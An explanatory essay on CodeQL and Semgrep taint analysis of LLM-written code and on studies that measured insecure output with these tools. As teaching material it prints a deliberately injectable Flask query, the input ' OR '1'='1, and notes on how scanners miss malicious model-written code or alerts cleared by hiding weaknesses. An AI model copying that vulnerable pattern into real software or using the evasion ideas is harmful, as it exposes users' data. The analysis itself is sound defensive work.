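# Running CodeQL and Semgrep taint analysis on code written by language models

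## How taint analysis works and what CodeQL and Semgrep ship with

Taint analysis checks, without running a program, whether data from one place in it can reach another place where that data would do harm. The textbook case is a web application that takes text a stranger typed into a form and passes it from function to function until it becomes part of a database command. A careful reader can trace that path by hand in a short program, but hardly anyone does in a large one, so engineers use tools.

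Two such tools are CodeQL, owned by the code-hosting company GitHub, and Semgrep, from a company of the same name. Both are static analyzers, which read source code without executing it, and both are older than the coding models whose output they now scan. Lunghi, Djire and colleagues (2026) explain in *Static Analysis Guidance for Secure LLM Code Generation* that generated code enters automated build pipelines with less human review, so an automatic check has to do some of the reviewer's work.

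### One flow, line by line

The program below uses Flask, a Python framework for web applications, to look up a customer's e-mail address by name. `request.args` holds whatever the visitor put in the web address.

```python
 1  import sqlite3
 2  from flask import Flask, request
 3  app = Flask(__name__)
 4  @app.route("/user")
 5  def show_user():
 6      name = request.args.get("name", "")
 7      key = name.strip()
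 8      query = "SELECT email FROM users WHERE name = '" + key + "'"
 9      cursor = sqlite3.connect("shop.db").cursor()
10      return str(cursor.execute(query).fetchall())
```

If a visitor sends `Ana`, the program returns Ana's address, but if the visitor sends `' OR '1'='1`, the input closes the quoted string early and makes the condition true for every row, so the program returns every address in the table. This weakness is called SQL injection and is number 89 in the Common Weakness Enumeration (CWE), a catalogue of software weakness types.

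Line 6 is the source, where the tracked data enters. Line 7 trims spaces from `name` and stores the result in `key`, which is tainted because it was computed from `name`. Any step that carries taint from one expression to another is a propagation step. GitHub's *About data flow analysis* distinguishes plain data flow, which follows a value only as long as it stays the same, from taint tracking, which also follows whatever the program computes from that value. Under taint tracking, if `x` is tainted, then `y` is tainted after `y = x + 1`. Line 8 is another propagation step because it makes `key` part of a longer string. Line 9 uses no tainted data. On line 10 the string becomes the first argument of `execute`, which is the sink, the operation tainted data should not reach. A taint analyzer that has followed these steps raises an alert.

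A sanitizer is a check or transformation after which the analyzer treats the data as safe. Converting `key` to an integer would be one example, if the column held numbers. The analyzer does not test whether a sanitizer works. According to Semgrep's *Taint analysis overview*, any expression that matches a rule's sanitizer pattern counts as clean. If a rule lists `sanitize_input(...)`, passing the data through a function of that name suppresses the alert, even if the function's body is empty.

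The normal fix for this program is to use query parameters rather than a sanitizer. GitHub's *SQL query built from user-controlled sources* recommends them, and here the call becomes `cursor.execute("SELECT email FROM users WHERE name = ?", (key,))`. The visitor's text still goes to the database, but as a second argument that the database library handles as plain data. The first argument is now a constant, so no taint reaches the sink.

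Nothing in these ten lines shows that `request.args` comes from an untrusted user or that `execute` runs its first argument as SQL. The analyzer gets that information from library models, which are hand-written descriptions it uses in place of library code it does not read. In CodeQL's Python analysis, a model can be a single row of data. GitHub's *Customizing Library Models for Python* gives the example `["flask", "Member[request]", "remote"]`, which marks the `request` member of every `flask` import as remote input. Other rows mark an argument as a particular kind of sink, such as `sql-injection`. Summary rows describe how taint passes through a call; the one for Python's `sorted` carries taint from the argument to the return value. If a library has no model, the analysis can miss a real flow.

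### How CodeQL finds the flow

CodeQL turns a program into a database, one for each language in the project, and searches the database rather than the program's text. According to GitHub's *About CodeQL*, an extractor for a compiled language watches the build and copies each file as the compiler receives it, while an extractor for an interpreted language such as Python works directly on the source files. Each database holds the syntax tree, the order in which statements can execute, and a data flow graph, whose nodes are things that carry values at run time and whose edges show where a value can go next.

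Queries then run against the database. Their language, QL, is declarative: the person who writes a query describes what a result looks like and leaves the search to the engine. A taint query for the program above needs little more than this, following the pattern in GitHub's *Analyzing data flow in Python*, with the import lines left out:

```ql
module RequestToSql implements DataFlow::ConfigSig {
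  predicate isSource(DataFlow::Node n) { n instanceof RemoteFlowSource }
  predicate isSink(DataFlow::Node n) { n = any(SqlExecution e).getSql() }
}
module Flow = TaintTracking::Global<RequestToSql>;

from DataFlow::Node source, DataFlow::Node sink
where Flow::flow(source, sink)
select sink, "This SQL statement depends on $@.", source, "request data"
```

`RemoteFlowSource` and `SqlExecution` are ready-made classes that collect the library models, so the same query covers Flask, Django and any other framework with a model. Two predicates are optional: `isBarrier` adds sanitizers, and `isAdditionalFlowStep` adds propagation steps.

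The word `Global` distinguishes this analysis from local data flow, which stays inside one function and is fast and fairly precise. Global data flow also follows calls between functions and values that the program stores in object properties, but it takes more time and memory and is somewhat less precise. GitHub's documentation lists three reasons the data flow graph is hard to get right: library source may be unavailable, some call targets are known only at run time, and two names can refer to the same object, so that a write through one changes the other.

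The query GitHub ships for this weakness, `py/sql-injection`, is a path query. It reports the whole route from source to sink, here lines 6, 7, 8 and 10, which a developer can step through when deciding whether the alert is real.

### How Semgrep finds it

Semgrep rules look like the code they match. A rule is a file in YAML, a plain-text configuration format, and the line `mode: taint` turns it from a search for a pattern into a search for a flow:

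```yaml
rules:
  - id: request-to-sql
    mode: taint
    languages: [python]
    severity: ERROR
    message: Request data reaches an SQL string
    pattern-sources:
      - pattern: flask.request.args.get(...)
    pattern-sinks:
      - patterns:
          - pattern: $CURSOR.execute($SQL, ...)
          - focus-metavariable: $SQL
```

The last line restricts the sink to the SQL string. Without that line, the rule would also flag the repaired program, which safely passes tainted data in the second argument.

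By default, Semgrep passes taint through assignments, operators and function calls, treating a call's output as tainted if any of its inputs is. CodeQL needs a model before it carries taint through a library call whose code it cannot analyze. Semgrep's default therefore misses fewer flows through unfamiliar functions, but it also marks some harmless results as tainted. If taint leaves a call another way, as when C's `strcpy` copies its second argument into its first, Semgrep needs a custom propagator, which only paying customers can write.

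Semgrep's free Community Edition also limits taint analysis to a single function. It can find the flow in the ten-line program because the source and sink are both in `show_user`. If a developer moves lines 9 and 10 into a helper, `run(query)`, the source and sink are in different functions, and the free edition reports nothing. The paid engine with the option `--pro-intrafile` follows taint across functions in one file and would report the flow. If the helper is then moved to another file, `db.py`, the scan needs the option `--pro`, a language with cross-file support, and a rule with `interfile: true` in its options. CodeQL's global analysis covers all three layouts.

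This limitation matters because most style guides ask for code to be split into small functions and files. Semgrep warns in its package description that the Community Edition "will miss many true positives" for this reason. The company has also published a comparison on Juice Shop, a web shop made deliberately insecure for training. It reports that the Community Edition found 21 of the flaws (44%) and the paid product 36 (75%), with no false positives from either. These are a vendor's figures for its own upgrade, they cover one application written by people, and cross-file tracking is only one of several differences between the products. Still, they make it important to check which edition produced any reported Semgrep result.

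### Checks that follow no data

Most of what people call static analysis is not taint analysis. Semgrep divides its rules into search rules, which are the default, and taint rules. A search rule reports code that matches a pattern, such as any call that starts a Flask server in debug mode. Semgrep works out constants and resolves imported names when it matches these patterns, but a search rule has no source or sink.

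Bandit, a free security linter for Python, works similarly. It builds a file's syntax tree and runs a set of plugins over it. In GitHub's *Python SQL Injection not being detected for CWE-089*, a 2024 thread on CodeQL's public issue tracker, a user complained that CodeQL had missed a function that Bandit flagged for assembling an SQL string from its arguments. A maintainer answered that building a string is safe in itself, and that CodeQL reports an injection only when user-controlled data gets into the string and the string is then executed. The code also turned out to use pandas, a data-analysis library for which CodeQL had no model, so CodeQL might well have missed the flow even if it was real. Bandit flags strings on less evidence than CodeQL and cannot distinguish dangerous ones from harmless ones, so it would have flagged this one either way.

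Secret scanners look for passwords and access keys left in the code. Semgrep's scanner, Semgrep Secrets, recognizes more than 630 types of credential and checks whether they still work by trying them against the services they belong to. It detects credentials where they appear in the code and doesn't trace where they go, as a taint rule would.

CodeQL's queries mix these approaches. The Python query for SQL injection tracks the flow of data, while "Flask app is run in debug mode" hardly needs to. Readers therefore can't learn much about taint analysis from a count of CodeQL alerts unless it is broken down by query.

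### Precision and recall

Two numbers describe how well an analyzer does. Precision is the share of flagged items that are truly bad, and recall is the share of truly bad items that the analyzer flags. Take 200 programs, of which 50 are vulnerable (the figures are invented):

| | Flagged | Not flagged |
|---|---|---|
| Truly vulnerable | 30 | 20 |
| Truly safe | 10 | 140 |

Precision is 30 out of 40, or 75%. Recall is 30 out of 50, or 60%.

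Precision is the easier of the two to measure, because a person can review the 40 flagged programs and judge each one. The 20 missed programs produced no alerts, so counting them requires an independent oracle, which is a verdict on security that comes from expert labels, security tests, or working attacks rather than from the analyzer under test. Without one, a result can look much better than it is. Lunghi and colleagues fed analyzer alerts to models while the models were writing code. On the RiskyPy benchmark, this significantly raised the share of working programs without alerts in all 12 comparisons, but the benchmark's independent judge confirmed a significant gain in security in only 2 of them.

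Precision also depends on how common bad programs are. The analyzer in the table catches 60% of bad programs and wrongly flags one safe program in fifteen. On 1,000 programs of which only 20 are bad, it would catch 12 and raise about 65 false alarms, so its precision would drop from 75% to about 16%. A rule that works well on SQL injection in web code could, with the same error rates, be close to useless for detecting a behaviour that occurs in one program in a thousand.

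### Query suites, precision labels and "off the shelf"

Almost all CodeQL users run a query suite, a set of queries that GitHub has put together, rather than picking queries individually. GitHub's *CodeQL query suites* describes two that come with the standard setup: `default`, which favours queries with few false positives, and `security-extended`, which adds queries of somewhat lower precision and severity. A third, `security-and-quality`, also includes queries unrelated to security. GitHub's *CodeQL query help for Python* lists "Unused import" and "Commented-out code" among them, so a count of all the alerts from this suite includes untidy code as well as vulnerabilities.

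Across all languages, CodeQL's default suite held 497 security queries covering 170 CWEs in July 2026, and the extended suite added 131 queries and 32 CWEs, according to GitHub's *CodeQL 2.26.1* (2026). The set for a single language is much smaller. GitHub's *Python queries for CodeQL analysis*, written for a server release that GitHub has since retired, lists 48 queries.

CodeQL suites select queries largely by the metadata in each query file, which includes a precision of low, medium, high or very high. Tweag (2025), a software consultancy, shows part of a CodeQL selector file that includes queries tagged "security" with high or very high precision. Changing a query's metadata can therefore change what a scan looks for. In April 2026, GitHub raised several C and C++ queries to high precision, and four of them joined the default suite as a result (GitHub, *CodeQL 2.25.3*, 2026).

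CodeQL's "high precision" label is an informed judgement by GitHub's staff, not a measured percentage. GitHub's *Metadata for CodeQL queries* defines precision as the percentage of results that are true positives. But GitHub's *Query file metadata and alert message style guide* says that staff add the label after testing, and that it "broadly" indicates the proportion of true positives, with context and relevance also considered. *Query classification and display*, an older document from the CodeQL project, states that the four precision labels have no fixed ranges. The label therefore doesn't give an expected true-positive rate for any particular body of code, let alone code from a language model, and it doesn't measure recall.

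"Off the shelf" means using only published queries or rules, without writing new sources or sinks. This includes running CodeQL's suites or the rules in Semgrep's public registry, and using options already built into the tools. It also includes using public rule sets that have to be fetched separately, such as the rules for malicious code that the security company Apiiro released and described in *Guard your Codebase*. A team doesn't get these rules just by turning the tool on, so anyone reporting a result that depends on them has to name them.

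The built-in rules also change over time. GitHub automatically deploys each new CodeQL version to users of code scanning on its site. In August 2026, it updated one JavaScript query to recognize another rate-limiting package, which can make an alert disappear from code that nobody has changed (GitHub, 2026). Two scans run a few months apart can therefore be compared only if the version used for each is recorded.

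### The author is trusted and the input is not

Nearly all the shipped taint queries are based on an implicit assumption that the programmer means well and that danger comes from outside.

CodeQL groups sources into threat models, and only `remote`, which covers data from the network, is on by default. Users can add a group that covers local files, command-line arguments, environment variables and database reads. According to GitHub's *Editing your configuration of default setup*, default setup offers this option only for Java, Kotlin and C#, so Python users have to configure it themselves. With the group added, an injection query checks whether a hostile value in an environment variable could reach an SQL string. It doesn't check whether a password stored in an environment variable could leak.

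File access is another example. The query in GitHub's *Uncontrolled data used in path expression* reports a JavaScript server that reads whatever file a web request names, because a visitor could ask for any file on the machine. If the path is instead a constant in the code, such as `tests/expected_output.json`, the query reports nothing, because no visitor can choose the file. The query does not check whether the author should have made the program open that file.

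The assumption is harmless for much model-written code. A model that writes the ten-line program above has made a mistake people have made for decades, the attacker is still a visitor to the website, and the shipped query fits. The query no longer fits when the model itself is under suspicion, for example because its code sends credentials to an outside server or opens the grader to look up the answer. In those cases the input may be safe, and the possible attacker is the model that wrote the code. Some shipped queries track sensitive data outward, such as into logs and stored files, but they too are designed to catch carelessness.

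People who hunt for malicious authors have had to write their own queries. In *GENIE*, Gobbi and Kinder (2024) used CodeQL to look for malware in npm, the public registry of JavaScript packages. They started from packages that npm had removed, worked out by hand what each one did, and wrote 12 queries to find similar behavior. In one simplified example, the sources are the computer's host name, home directory and user details, and the sink is data written to an outgoing web request. A flow from just one of these sources turned out to be too weak a sign, so the real query requires flows from all three. The 12 queries found 125 previously unreported malicious packages, with no false alarms. I think this is the best evidence both that CodeQL's engine can be used to detect malicious authors and that someone first has to describe what such an author does. After the 2020 attack on the software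 maker SolarWinds, in which intruders inserted malicious code into the company's builds, GitHub likewise published the detection queries as a separate pack, called them a heuristic, and warned that a clean result did not rule out compromise.

### Four conditions for a catch

An off-the-shelf taint scan stops a piece of bad behaviour in model-written code only if four conditions all hold. If each held 80% of the time, given that the earlier ones held, the scan would stop about 41% of cases.

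1. The behaviour has to be a flow, with data that starts in one place and does harm in another. A page that shows anyone's invoices because the model forgot to check who is asking contains no forbidden flow, only a missing check. Lunghi and colleagues put missing authorization checks and flawed business logic beyond the reach of pattern-based rules, and a plain source-to-sink query does no better with them. On SecEvalPlus, a benchmark where many of the weaknesses have no recognizable pattern, they found that Semgrep and Bandit flagged at most 5.6% of the programs that worked but were insecure. They did not run CodeQL there.

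2. A shipped query has to name both the source and the sink. Having one of them is no help. CodeQL has classes for file access and for remote input, and its path query still passes over the constant path to a test file, since it looks only for the two in combination.

3. The analyzer has to be able to follow the data the whole way. The helper function `run(query)` is enough to defeat free Semgrep, and an unmodelled library can defeat CodeQL. Nobody need intend this. An author who did intend it would have plenty to choose from: Gobbi and Kinder list ordinary JavaScript disguises that break CodeQL's tracking, among them computing a property's name at run time where a programmer would normally write it out.

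4. Someone has to read the alert and do the right thing about it. Increasingly that someone is another model, or the same one. On BaxBench, a benchmark of small web servers, the task requires each server to accept connections from outside its container, and a Semgrep rule objects to exactly that setting. The prompt told the models to put the task first. In 79 of 83 cases they obeyed the alert and removed the setting, and a server that nobody can reach passes no functional tests.

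## What studies of Copilot and its successors counted with CodeQL

In June 2021, GitHub released Copilot, an assistant that suggests code while a programmer types. Researchers soon began running CodeQL on its suggestions, and later on the output of other models, to find out how often the code was insecure. These researchers use CodeQL to evaluate the models and mostly take its results as given.

### A sample containing a weakness

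Nearly all of these studies count the samples that contain at least one weakness, so a sample with several weaknesses counts once. A sample is one program, file or completion that a model wrote, and a weakness is code that matches an entry in the CWE catalogue.

An alert is only CodeQL's report of a possible weakness. The tool may raise three alerts on one sample, one on a harmless line, or none on a sample with an obvious weakness. A weakness is an exploitable vulnerability only if an attacker can reach the weak line and gain something there. The ten-line Flask program with the SQL injection contains a weakness wherever it runs, but it isn't exploitable if it runs only on its author's laptop with invented customers. In *Asleep at the Keyboard?*, Pearce, Ahmad and colleagues (2021) explicitly set exploitability aside and judged only whether each program definitely contained the weakness being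 tested for.

### Copilot in 2021

Pearce and colleagues wrote 54 short, unfinished programs, or "scenarios", in C and Python. These covered 18 of the 25 weakness types that MITRE, which maintains the CWE catalogue, had ranked most dangerous that year. No scenario contained a weakness at the start, but a naive completion could introduce one. For instance, one scenario calls for a web handler that deletes a visitor's e-mail address from a database.

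Copilot, then a technical preview, supplied up to 25 completions per scenario. The researchers discarded those that would not compile or parse and judged 477 of the remaining 1,084 programs (44%) vulnerable. The rate was 50% in C and 38% in Python. Copilot's top-ranked suggestion was vulnerable in 24 scenarios. The study's better-known figure of about 40% also includes variations on a single prompt and a set of hardware designs.

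Several rules lowered the count. CodeQL checked only for the weakness each scenario targeted, so a login handler with safe SQL and an unprotected password passed the SQL scenario. Unfinished code counted as safe, so if Copilot pasted user input into an SQL string but stopped before executing it, that did not count as an injection. The researchers also gave Copilot the benefit of the doubt when it called a function that did not exist. The choice of scenarios raised the count, since each one made a mistake easy. And 28 of the 54 came from CodeQL's own examples and documentation, which the researchers preferred because CodeQL could evaluate them with little extra work. The 44% therefore does not estimate how often Copilot's everyday suggestions were weak.

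According to the results tables, the authors, rather than CodeQL, marked 14 of the 54 scenarios. Those 14 account for 270 of the programs and 130 of the 477 weak ones. They include every scenario on unrestricted file uploads (CWE-434), missing authentication (CWE-306), information exposure (CWE-200) and poorly protected credentials (CWE-522). In two of the information-exposure scenarios, the task is to write a login page. In one of them, a completion is weak if it gives different messages for a wrong username and a wrong password, because an attacker can then work out which usernames exist. An ordinary taint query would not detect this weakness, because no tainted data reaches a sink.

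People made 108 of the 219 weak verdicts in Python, so almost half of the Python result is not evidence of what CodeQL can detect. This gap in the evidence includes the two categories closest to leaking secrets.

A further experiment varied one Python prompt in 17 ways and used CodeQL to make every judgment. With the original prompt, 6 of 25 completions allowed SQL injection, but the same model's results changed with the surrounding code. When the researchers added a safe database function elsewhere in the file, 0 of 18 completions were vulnerable, and when they added an unsafe one, 17 of 18 were.

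### The same scenarios on later models

Majdinasab, Bishop and colleagues (2023), in *Assessing the Security of GitHub Copilot's Generated Code*, repeated the 29 Python scenarios with a newer Copilot and a newer CodeQL. They reported that the share of weak suggestions had fallen from 36.54% to 27.25%, or 112 of 411 by their results table. (The original Python figure was 38.35%. The lower one seems to come from a copying slip, with 1 weak program in place of 11 in one scenario.)

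The method of judging suggestions had changed along with the model. Pearce and colleagues had used custom queries for hard-coded credentials and for one path-traversal scenario, in which a program unpacks an archive. Those queries no longer ran on the newer CodeQL, so Majdinasab and colleagues substituted others, which found nothing in any of the four scenarios. Both studies judged poorly protected credentials by hand, but Pearce and colleagues had marked passwords hashed with MD5 or a single round of SHA-256 as weak, while Majdinasab and colleagues did not consider the strength of the hashing algorithm. In the three scenarios on poorly protected credentials, weak suggestions fell from 40 of 61 to 3 of 46.

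Without these seven scenarios, the pooled rate is 34% in the original study and 35% in the replication. If each scenario counts equally, the rate still falls, from 36% to 27%. The two calculations differ because the newer Copilot gave between 1 and 32 distinct, usable suggestions per scenario, so some scenarios count much more than others in the pooled rate. Some of the improvement in the omitted scenarios may also be real, since GitHub had announced a filter in February 2023 for hard-coded credentials, SQL injection and path injection. But the headline fall of nine percentage points combines a change in Copilot with changes in how the studies measured vulnerabilities.

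The 17 Python scenarios that CodeQL assessed in both studies allow a cleaner comparison. The share of vulnerable completions in these scenarios was 33% for the 2021 Copilot and 28% for its successor. In *From Model to Breach*, Vallez, Sternfeld and colleagues (2025) ran the same scenarios on 15 open-weight models, after correcting errors in four scenarios and rearranging some so that a model could continue directly from the end of the prompt. CodeQL found the target weakness in 10.4% of valid completions from CodeGemma 7B Instruct, the lowest share, and 37.4% from CodeLlama 70B Instruct, the highest.

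Vallez and colleagues conclude that the security of open-weight coding models has hardly changed in three years. That seems too pessimistic about the best models, since the instruction-tuned versions of CodeGemma, Qwen2.5-Coder and StarCoder-2 all had vulnerability rates between 10% and 12%. But when the researchers rewrote the scenarios as English requests and rephrased each one ten ways, those three models' rates rose to between 14% and 18%, and Qwen3-Coder's rose from 18% to 27%.

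The kinds of weakness also changed, which the totals don't show. Vallez and colleagues gave each prompt an exposure score from 0 to 10, which combines how severe the weakness is, how often the model produces it and how likely people are to phrase the request that way. No model scored above 1.6 on any of the three SQL injection prompts, but all seven scored 6.9 or 7.0 on one of the two path-traversal prompts.

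### Files from public repositories

In *Security Weaknesses of Copilot-Generated Code in GitHub Projects*, Fu, Liang and colleagues (2023) looked for generated code that people had kept, because prompts that invite mistakes show what a model can get wrong but not what ends up in real projects. They searched GitHub for phrases such as "by GitHub Copilot", read through the results and selected files whose comments credited an assistant. They also included all the Python and JavaScript files from projects described as entirely generated, but excluded solutions to programming exercises.

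The enlarged 2025 version of the study covers 733 files, 672 from Copilot and the rest from CodeWhisperer and Codeium. Fu and colleagues scanned every file with CodeQL's `security-and-quality` suite and with either Bandit (for Python) or ESLint (for JavaScript). Two authors then checked the findings independently. They discarded false alarms and any weaknesses in code that a person seemed to have written. That left 200 files (27.3%) with at least one weakness, and the rate was slightly higher for Python than for JavaScript. Majdinasab and colleagues cite a rate of about 36% from an earlier version of the study, so the figure depends a good deal on which files the search finds.

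The figure also includes results from Bandit, which doesn't trace data flow and reported 235 of the security issues. The most common weakness was the use of insufficiently random numbers, with 114 of 628 instances. The list also includes dead code and function calls with the wrong number of arguments, which have CWE entries but which many security teams would not call security problems.

Schreiber and Tippe found a lower rate in a larger sample of 7,703 files from public GitHub repositories, all attributed to an AI coding tool. In *Securing AI-Generated Code*, Surikov (2026) reports that 12.1% of files had at least one detectable CWE, but he gives the figure in a sentence about Python having the highest rates, so it is unclear whether it covers all languages. Both studies rely on people who say that an AI wrote their code, and these people may not be typical. In Fu and colleagues' sample,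 most of them had small projects with few followers.

### Wider counts in 2025 and 2026

Most of this work concerns Python, but *LLM-CSEC* (Shahid, Ahmed and Ranjan, 2025) covers C and C++, with 84 prompts based on MITRE's weakness descriptions. The ten models tested, all old by now, included GPT-3.5 Turbo, Gemini 1.5 Pro, and Llama and Mistral models small enough to run locally. Each model answered every prompt twice, once as a plain assistant and once with an instruction to write secure code.

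CodeQL's `security-extended` suite flagged between 5% and 35% of the files. The security instruction lowered the share for four models, raised it for two and left it unchanged for four. Most findings were unchecked return values, followed by buffer errors. The counts for two return-value weaknesses, CWE-252 and CWE-253, are almost identical for every model, which suggests that one alert often carries both labels. If so, adding up CWE counts would count some mistakes twice.

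Morkonda, Selim and Assal (2026) report the highest rates in *Security of LLM-generated Code*. They gave 81 Python prompts to seven tools: Claude 3, GPT-4o, Gemini, Perplexity, Phind-70B, CodeWhisperer and IBM's watsonx. Depending on the tool, between 73% and 90% of the 81 programs had at least one vulnerability. They checked every program for all 12 of their weakness types, whereas Pearce and colleagues checked each program for only one.

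Of the 995 vulnerabilities, 381 fell under information exposure, and 69% of those were Flask applications with debug mode switched on, which lets a visitor run code on the server if the developer leaves it on. Most of the information-exposure findings came from prompts about something else, so the narrower 2021 check would not have counted them. Debug mode accounts for nearly half of CodeQL's 559 findings, and CodeWhisperer, whose code never switched it on, had the fewest vulnerabilities of the seven.

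The other 436 findings came from GPT-4o. The researchers asked it to look for six weakness types, including SQL injection, because CodeQL's queries had found no instances of them. GPT-4o was also one of the tools under test. Some of its findings look doubtful. It reported 20 cases of unsafe deserialization, the loading of untrusted data into program objects, although the researchers saw no call to an unsafe loading function in any of the code. Some of the programs it flagged for SQL injection used query parameters, the standard fix.

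Surikov tested newer models on 26 Python prompts, running each prompt many times. CodeQL or Bandit reported at least one finding in 46% of first drafts from Claude Opus 4.8, 53% from Sonnet 4.6, 65% from Sonnet 5 and 69% from Haiku 4.5.

| Study | Code | What decides that a sample is weak | Share weak |
|---|---|---|---|
| Pearce and colleagues | Copilot preview; C and Python | CodeQL or the authors, one target weakness | 44% |
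| Majdinasab and colleagues | Later Copilot; Python | CodeQL or the authors, one target weakness | 27% |
| Vallez and colleagues | 15 open-weight models; Python | CodeQL, one target weakness | 10–37% |
| Fu and colleagues | Copilot and two others, GitHub files; Python and JavaScript | CodeQL and a second tool, any weakness, then manual review | 27% |
| Schreiber and Tippe | AI-attributed GitHub files | Any detectable CWE | 12% |
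| Shahid and colleagues | Ten older models; C and C++ | CodeQL, any weakness in the suite | 5–35% |
| Morkonda and colleagues | Seven older tools; Python | CodeQL or GPT-4o, any of 12 weaknesses | 73–90% |
| Surikov | Four Claude models; Python | CodeQL or Bandit, any finding | 46–69% |

The rates in the last column do not establish a trend over time. The newest models have higher rates than the 2021 Copilot, but under a broader counting rule. The rates for the two GitHub samples differ by a factor of two, even though people had accepted the code in both.

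### From fewer findings to safer code

Suppose CodeQL reports findings in 30 of 100 programs from one model and in 20 of 100 from another. The second model may well write safer code, but that conclusion depends on assumptions that could each be false independently of the others.

Two counts are comparable only if they were measured the same way. The Copilot replication shows how easily this condition fails when years pass between scans. Within a single study, researchers usually meet it by giving every model the same prompts and running the same version of the same queries, so any faults in CodeQL stay constant. The comparison is most convincing when the model also stays the same. Pearce and colleagues found 0 weak completions out of 18 with safe code nearby and 17 out of 18 with unsafe code nearby, a difference that a quirk of CodeQL is unlikely to explain.

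The two models must also have produced comparable code. CodeQL analysed the C and C++ files in LLM-CSEC only if they compiled, but Shahid and colleagues kept the uncompiled files in the denominator, so files that failed to compile could lower a model's rate. Under the security instruction, Llama 2 produced files for only 62 of the 84 prompts, and CodeQL flagged 3 of those files, the lowest share in the study. Shahid and colleagues ask whether such a result reflects better security or just less code.

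Vallez and colleagues avoid part of this problem by counting only valid completions, which made up at least 95% of every model's output. However, a program can parse and still not do its job. Program length also affects the comparison. Watsonx had the second-fewest vulnerabilities in Morkonda and colleagues' comparison but the most per line, because it wrote the shortest programs. Its function for pinging a web address was seven lines long and passed the address directly to the operating system, while CodeWhisperer's was 43 lines long and included checks on the input.

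A more doubtful assumption is that the prompts represent the work people give these models. Morkonda and colleagues and Surikov both took their prompts from LLMSecEval, a public collection in which other researchers rewrote Pearce and colleagues' scenarios in plain English. The replication and the open-weight study also used prompts derived from those scenarios, so four later studies rely on one set written in 2021. Sharing the scenarios makes the studies easier to compare, but it also gives developers time to train models on them, deliberately or not. Surikov lists this as a limitation. A model that has learned to handle these 54 well-known scenarios may not have improved much on other tasks.

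The studies' strongest safeguards are against counting findings that aren't real weaknesses. Pearce and colleagues' conservative labels kept unfinished code and unknown functions out of the count, and Fu and colleagues read every finding before accepting it. Surikov did neither, and so takes a clean scan to mean only that the tools found no known pattern. Where nobody has reviewed the alerts, one model can look worse merely because its style triggers more false alarms.

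Even if every finding is real, a count can misrepresent danger if it ignores severity. Surikov's tally counts an SQL injection and a minor warning equally. Among the seven models that Vallez and colleagues scored for exposure, CodeLlama 70B Instruct had the highest share of weak code but the best exposure score, partly because many of its mistakes were of the least severe type in the test. Their severity weights only partly solve the problem, because each weight is an average for a whole weakness type and doesn't account for where a particular program will run.

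Comparing two models by their CodeQL findings assumes that CodeQL misses the same share of weaknesses in both models' code, and these studies can do less about this assumption than about any other. In the earlier example of two models with 30 and 20 findings, each might in fact have written 40 weak programs. If the second model often uses a database library for which CodeQL has no library model, CodeQL may catch 30 of the first model's weak programs and only 20 of the second's. The second model would then look a third better, although both are equally unsafe. Using the same tool on both models cancels only errors that affect them equally, and this error varies with how each model writes code. Manual review of alerts doesn't reveal the weaknesses that CodeQL missed. The studies had an independent check only in the scenarios that people judged by hand, and those scenarios had no CodeQL verdict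 to compare it with.

The choice of analyzer seems to affect the results. Shahid and colleagues also scanned their files with Snyk Code and Meta's CodeShield, and no weakness type appeared in the results of all three tools. Snyk Code found nothing in Gemini 1.5 Pro's code, although CodeQL had flagged about a third of the files.

A drop in alerts is the weakest evidence of safer code when the model has seen the tool's alerts. When Fu and colleagues asked Copilot Chat to repair 295 weaknesses, 32% disappeared on a second scan after a general request, and 55.5% after a request that included the warnings. In Surikov's experiment, adding the scanners' findings to the repair prompt increased the average reduction from 42% to 57%. In both cases the same tools supplied the warnings and checked the repairs, and a model can clear an alert by removing the weakness or by writing it in a form the tools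 do not detect. Lunghi and colleagues also used an independent judge, which confirmed few of the gains that their alert counts had suggested.

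## Precision and recall when the answer is known independently

Every count so far leaves out the weaknesses that CodeQL missed, and running CodeQL again can't find them. If a team defines insecure code as code with a CodeQL alert, CodeQL scores 100% on both precision and recall, however bad its queries are, because the flagged programs and the insecure programs are the same by definition.

Checking alerts by hand measures only precision. For *An Empirical Analysis of CodeQL False Positives and Query Refinements* (2026), reviewers traced reported paths through Java projects and recorded why each false alarm was not an exploitable vulnerability. This kind of review can also lead to better queries.

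Much of the research on generated code does not measure recall. Firouzi and Ghafari (2026), in *Persistent Human Feedback, LLMs, and Static Analyzers for Secure Code Generation*, looked at nine studies of secure code generation published in leading software engineering venues in 2025. Five of the nine used CodeQL as a security checker, and four involved no manual inspection. Firouzi and Ghafari labelled 1,080 programs by hand and compared the results from CodeQL and Semgrep with those labels.

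### Who or what decides that code is insecure

Hand labels are one of several independent oracles in use, and each has its own blind spots.

How well experts agree on whether a program is vulnerable depends on what they have to decide. In Firouzi and Ghafari's study, a doctoral student and a master's student, supervised by a faculty expert, decided whether each program contained the one weakness its task was designed to provoke. One labelled all 1,080 programs and the other independently labelled 108. Their agreement was 0.94 on Cohen's kappa, where 1 is perfect agreement and 0 is the agreement expected by chance. Lunghi and colleagues asked two engineers, with seven and eight years of experience, the broader question of whether a program contained any vulnerability that someone could exploit in context. The engineers agreed on 33 of 50 programs, a kappa of 0.36. One considered 30 of the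 programs secure and the other only 17. The narrow question gives more reliable labels, but a program labelled free of the target weakness may still contain a different one.

Security tests send hostile input to a program and check how it responds. They give the same result every time, but they cover only the attacks their author thought of. A test may also fail a safe program that rejects bad input in an unexpected way.

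Testing with live exploits goes further by attacking the running application. A successful exploit is strong evidence of a vulnerability, but a failed one proves little, since attacks also fail when the server never starts. Lunghi and colleagues therefore compared alerts with exploits only on applications that passed their functional tests.

A solver can prove that a dangerous condition is possible. *Broken by Default* (Blain and Noiseux, 2026) uses Z3, a program that searches for values satisfying a set of logical and arithmetic conditions. One example is the C expression `malloc(n * sizeof(int))`, which is meant to reserve memory for `n` four-byte integers. Z3 looks for a 32-bit `n` for which the product is smaller than `n`. One solution is 2³⁰ + 1. Multiplying it by four gives 2³² + 4, but 32-bit arithmetic drops the 2³² and leaves 4. The program then reserves enough memory for only one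 integer and may write more than a billion integers to it.

The arithmetic is certain, but the formula in the proof lets `n` take any value, so the proof does not establish that an attacker can choose it. On a 64-bit machine, where memory sizes have 64 bits, multiplying a 32-bit `n` by four does not wrap around. Blain and Noiseux built demonstrations for seven selected findings, and six worked, but the demonstrations included a SQL injection and a cracked password hash as well as memory errors. Blain and Noiseux also founded Cobalt AI and ran the analysis with their own tool, COBALT.

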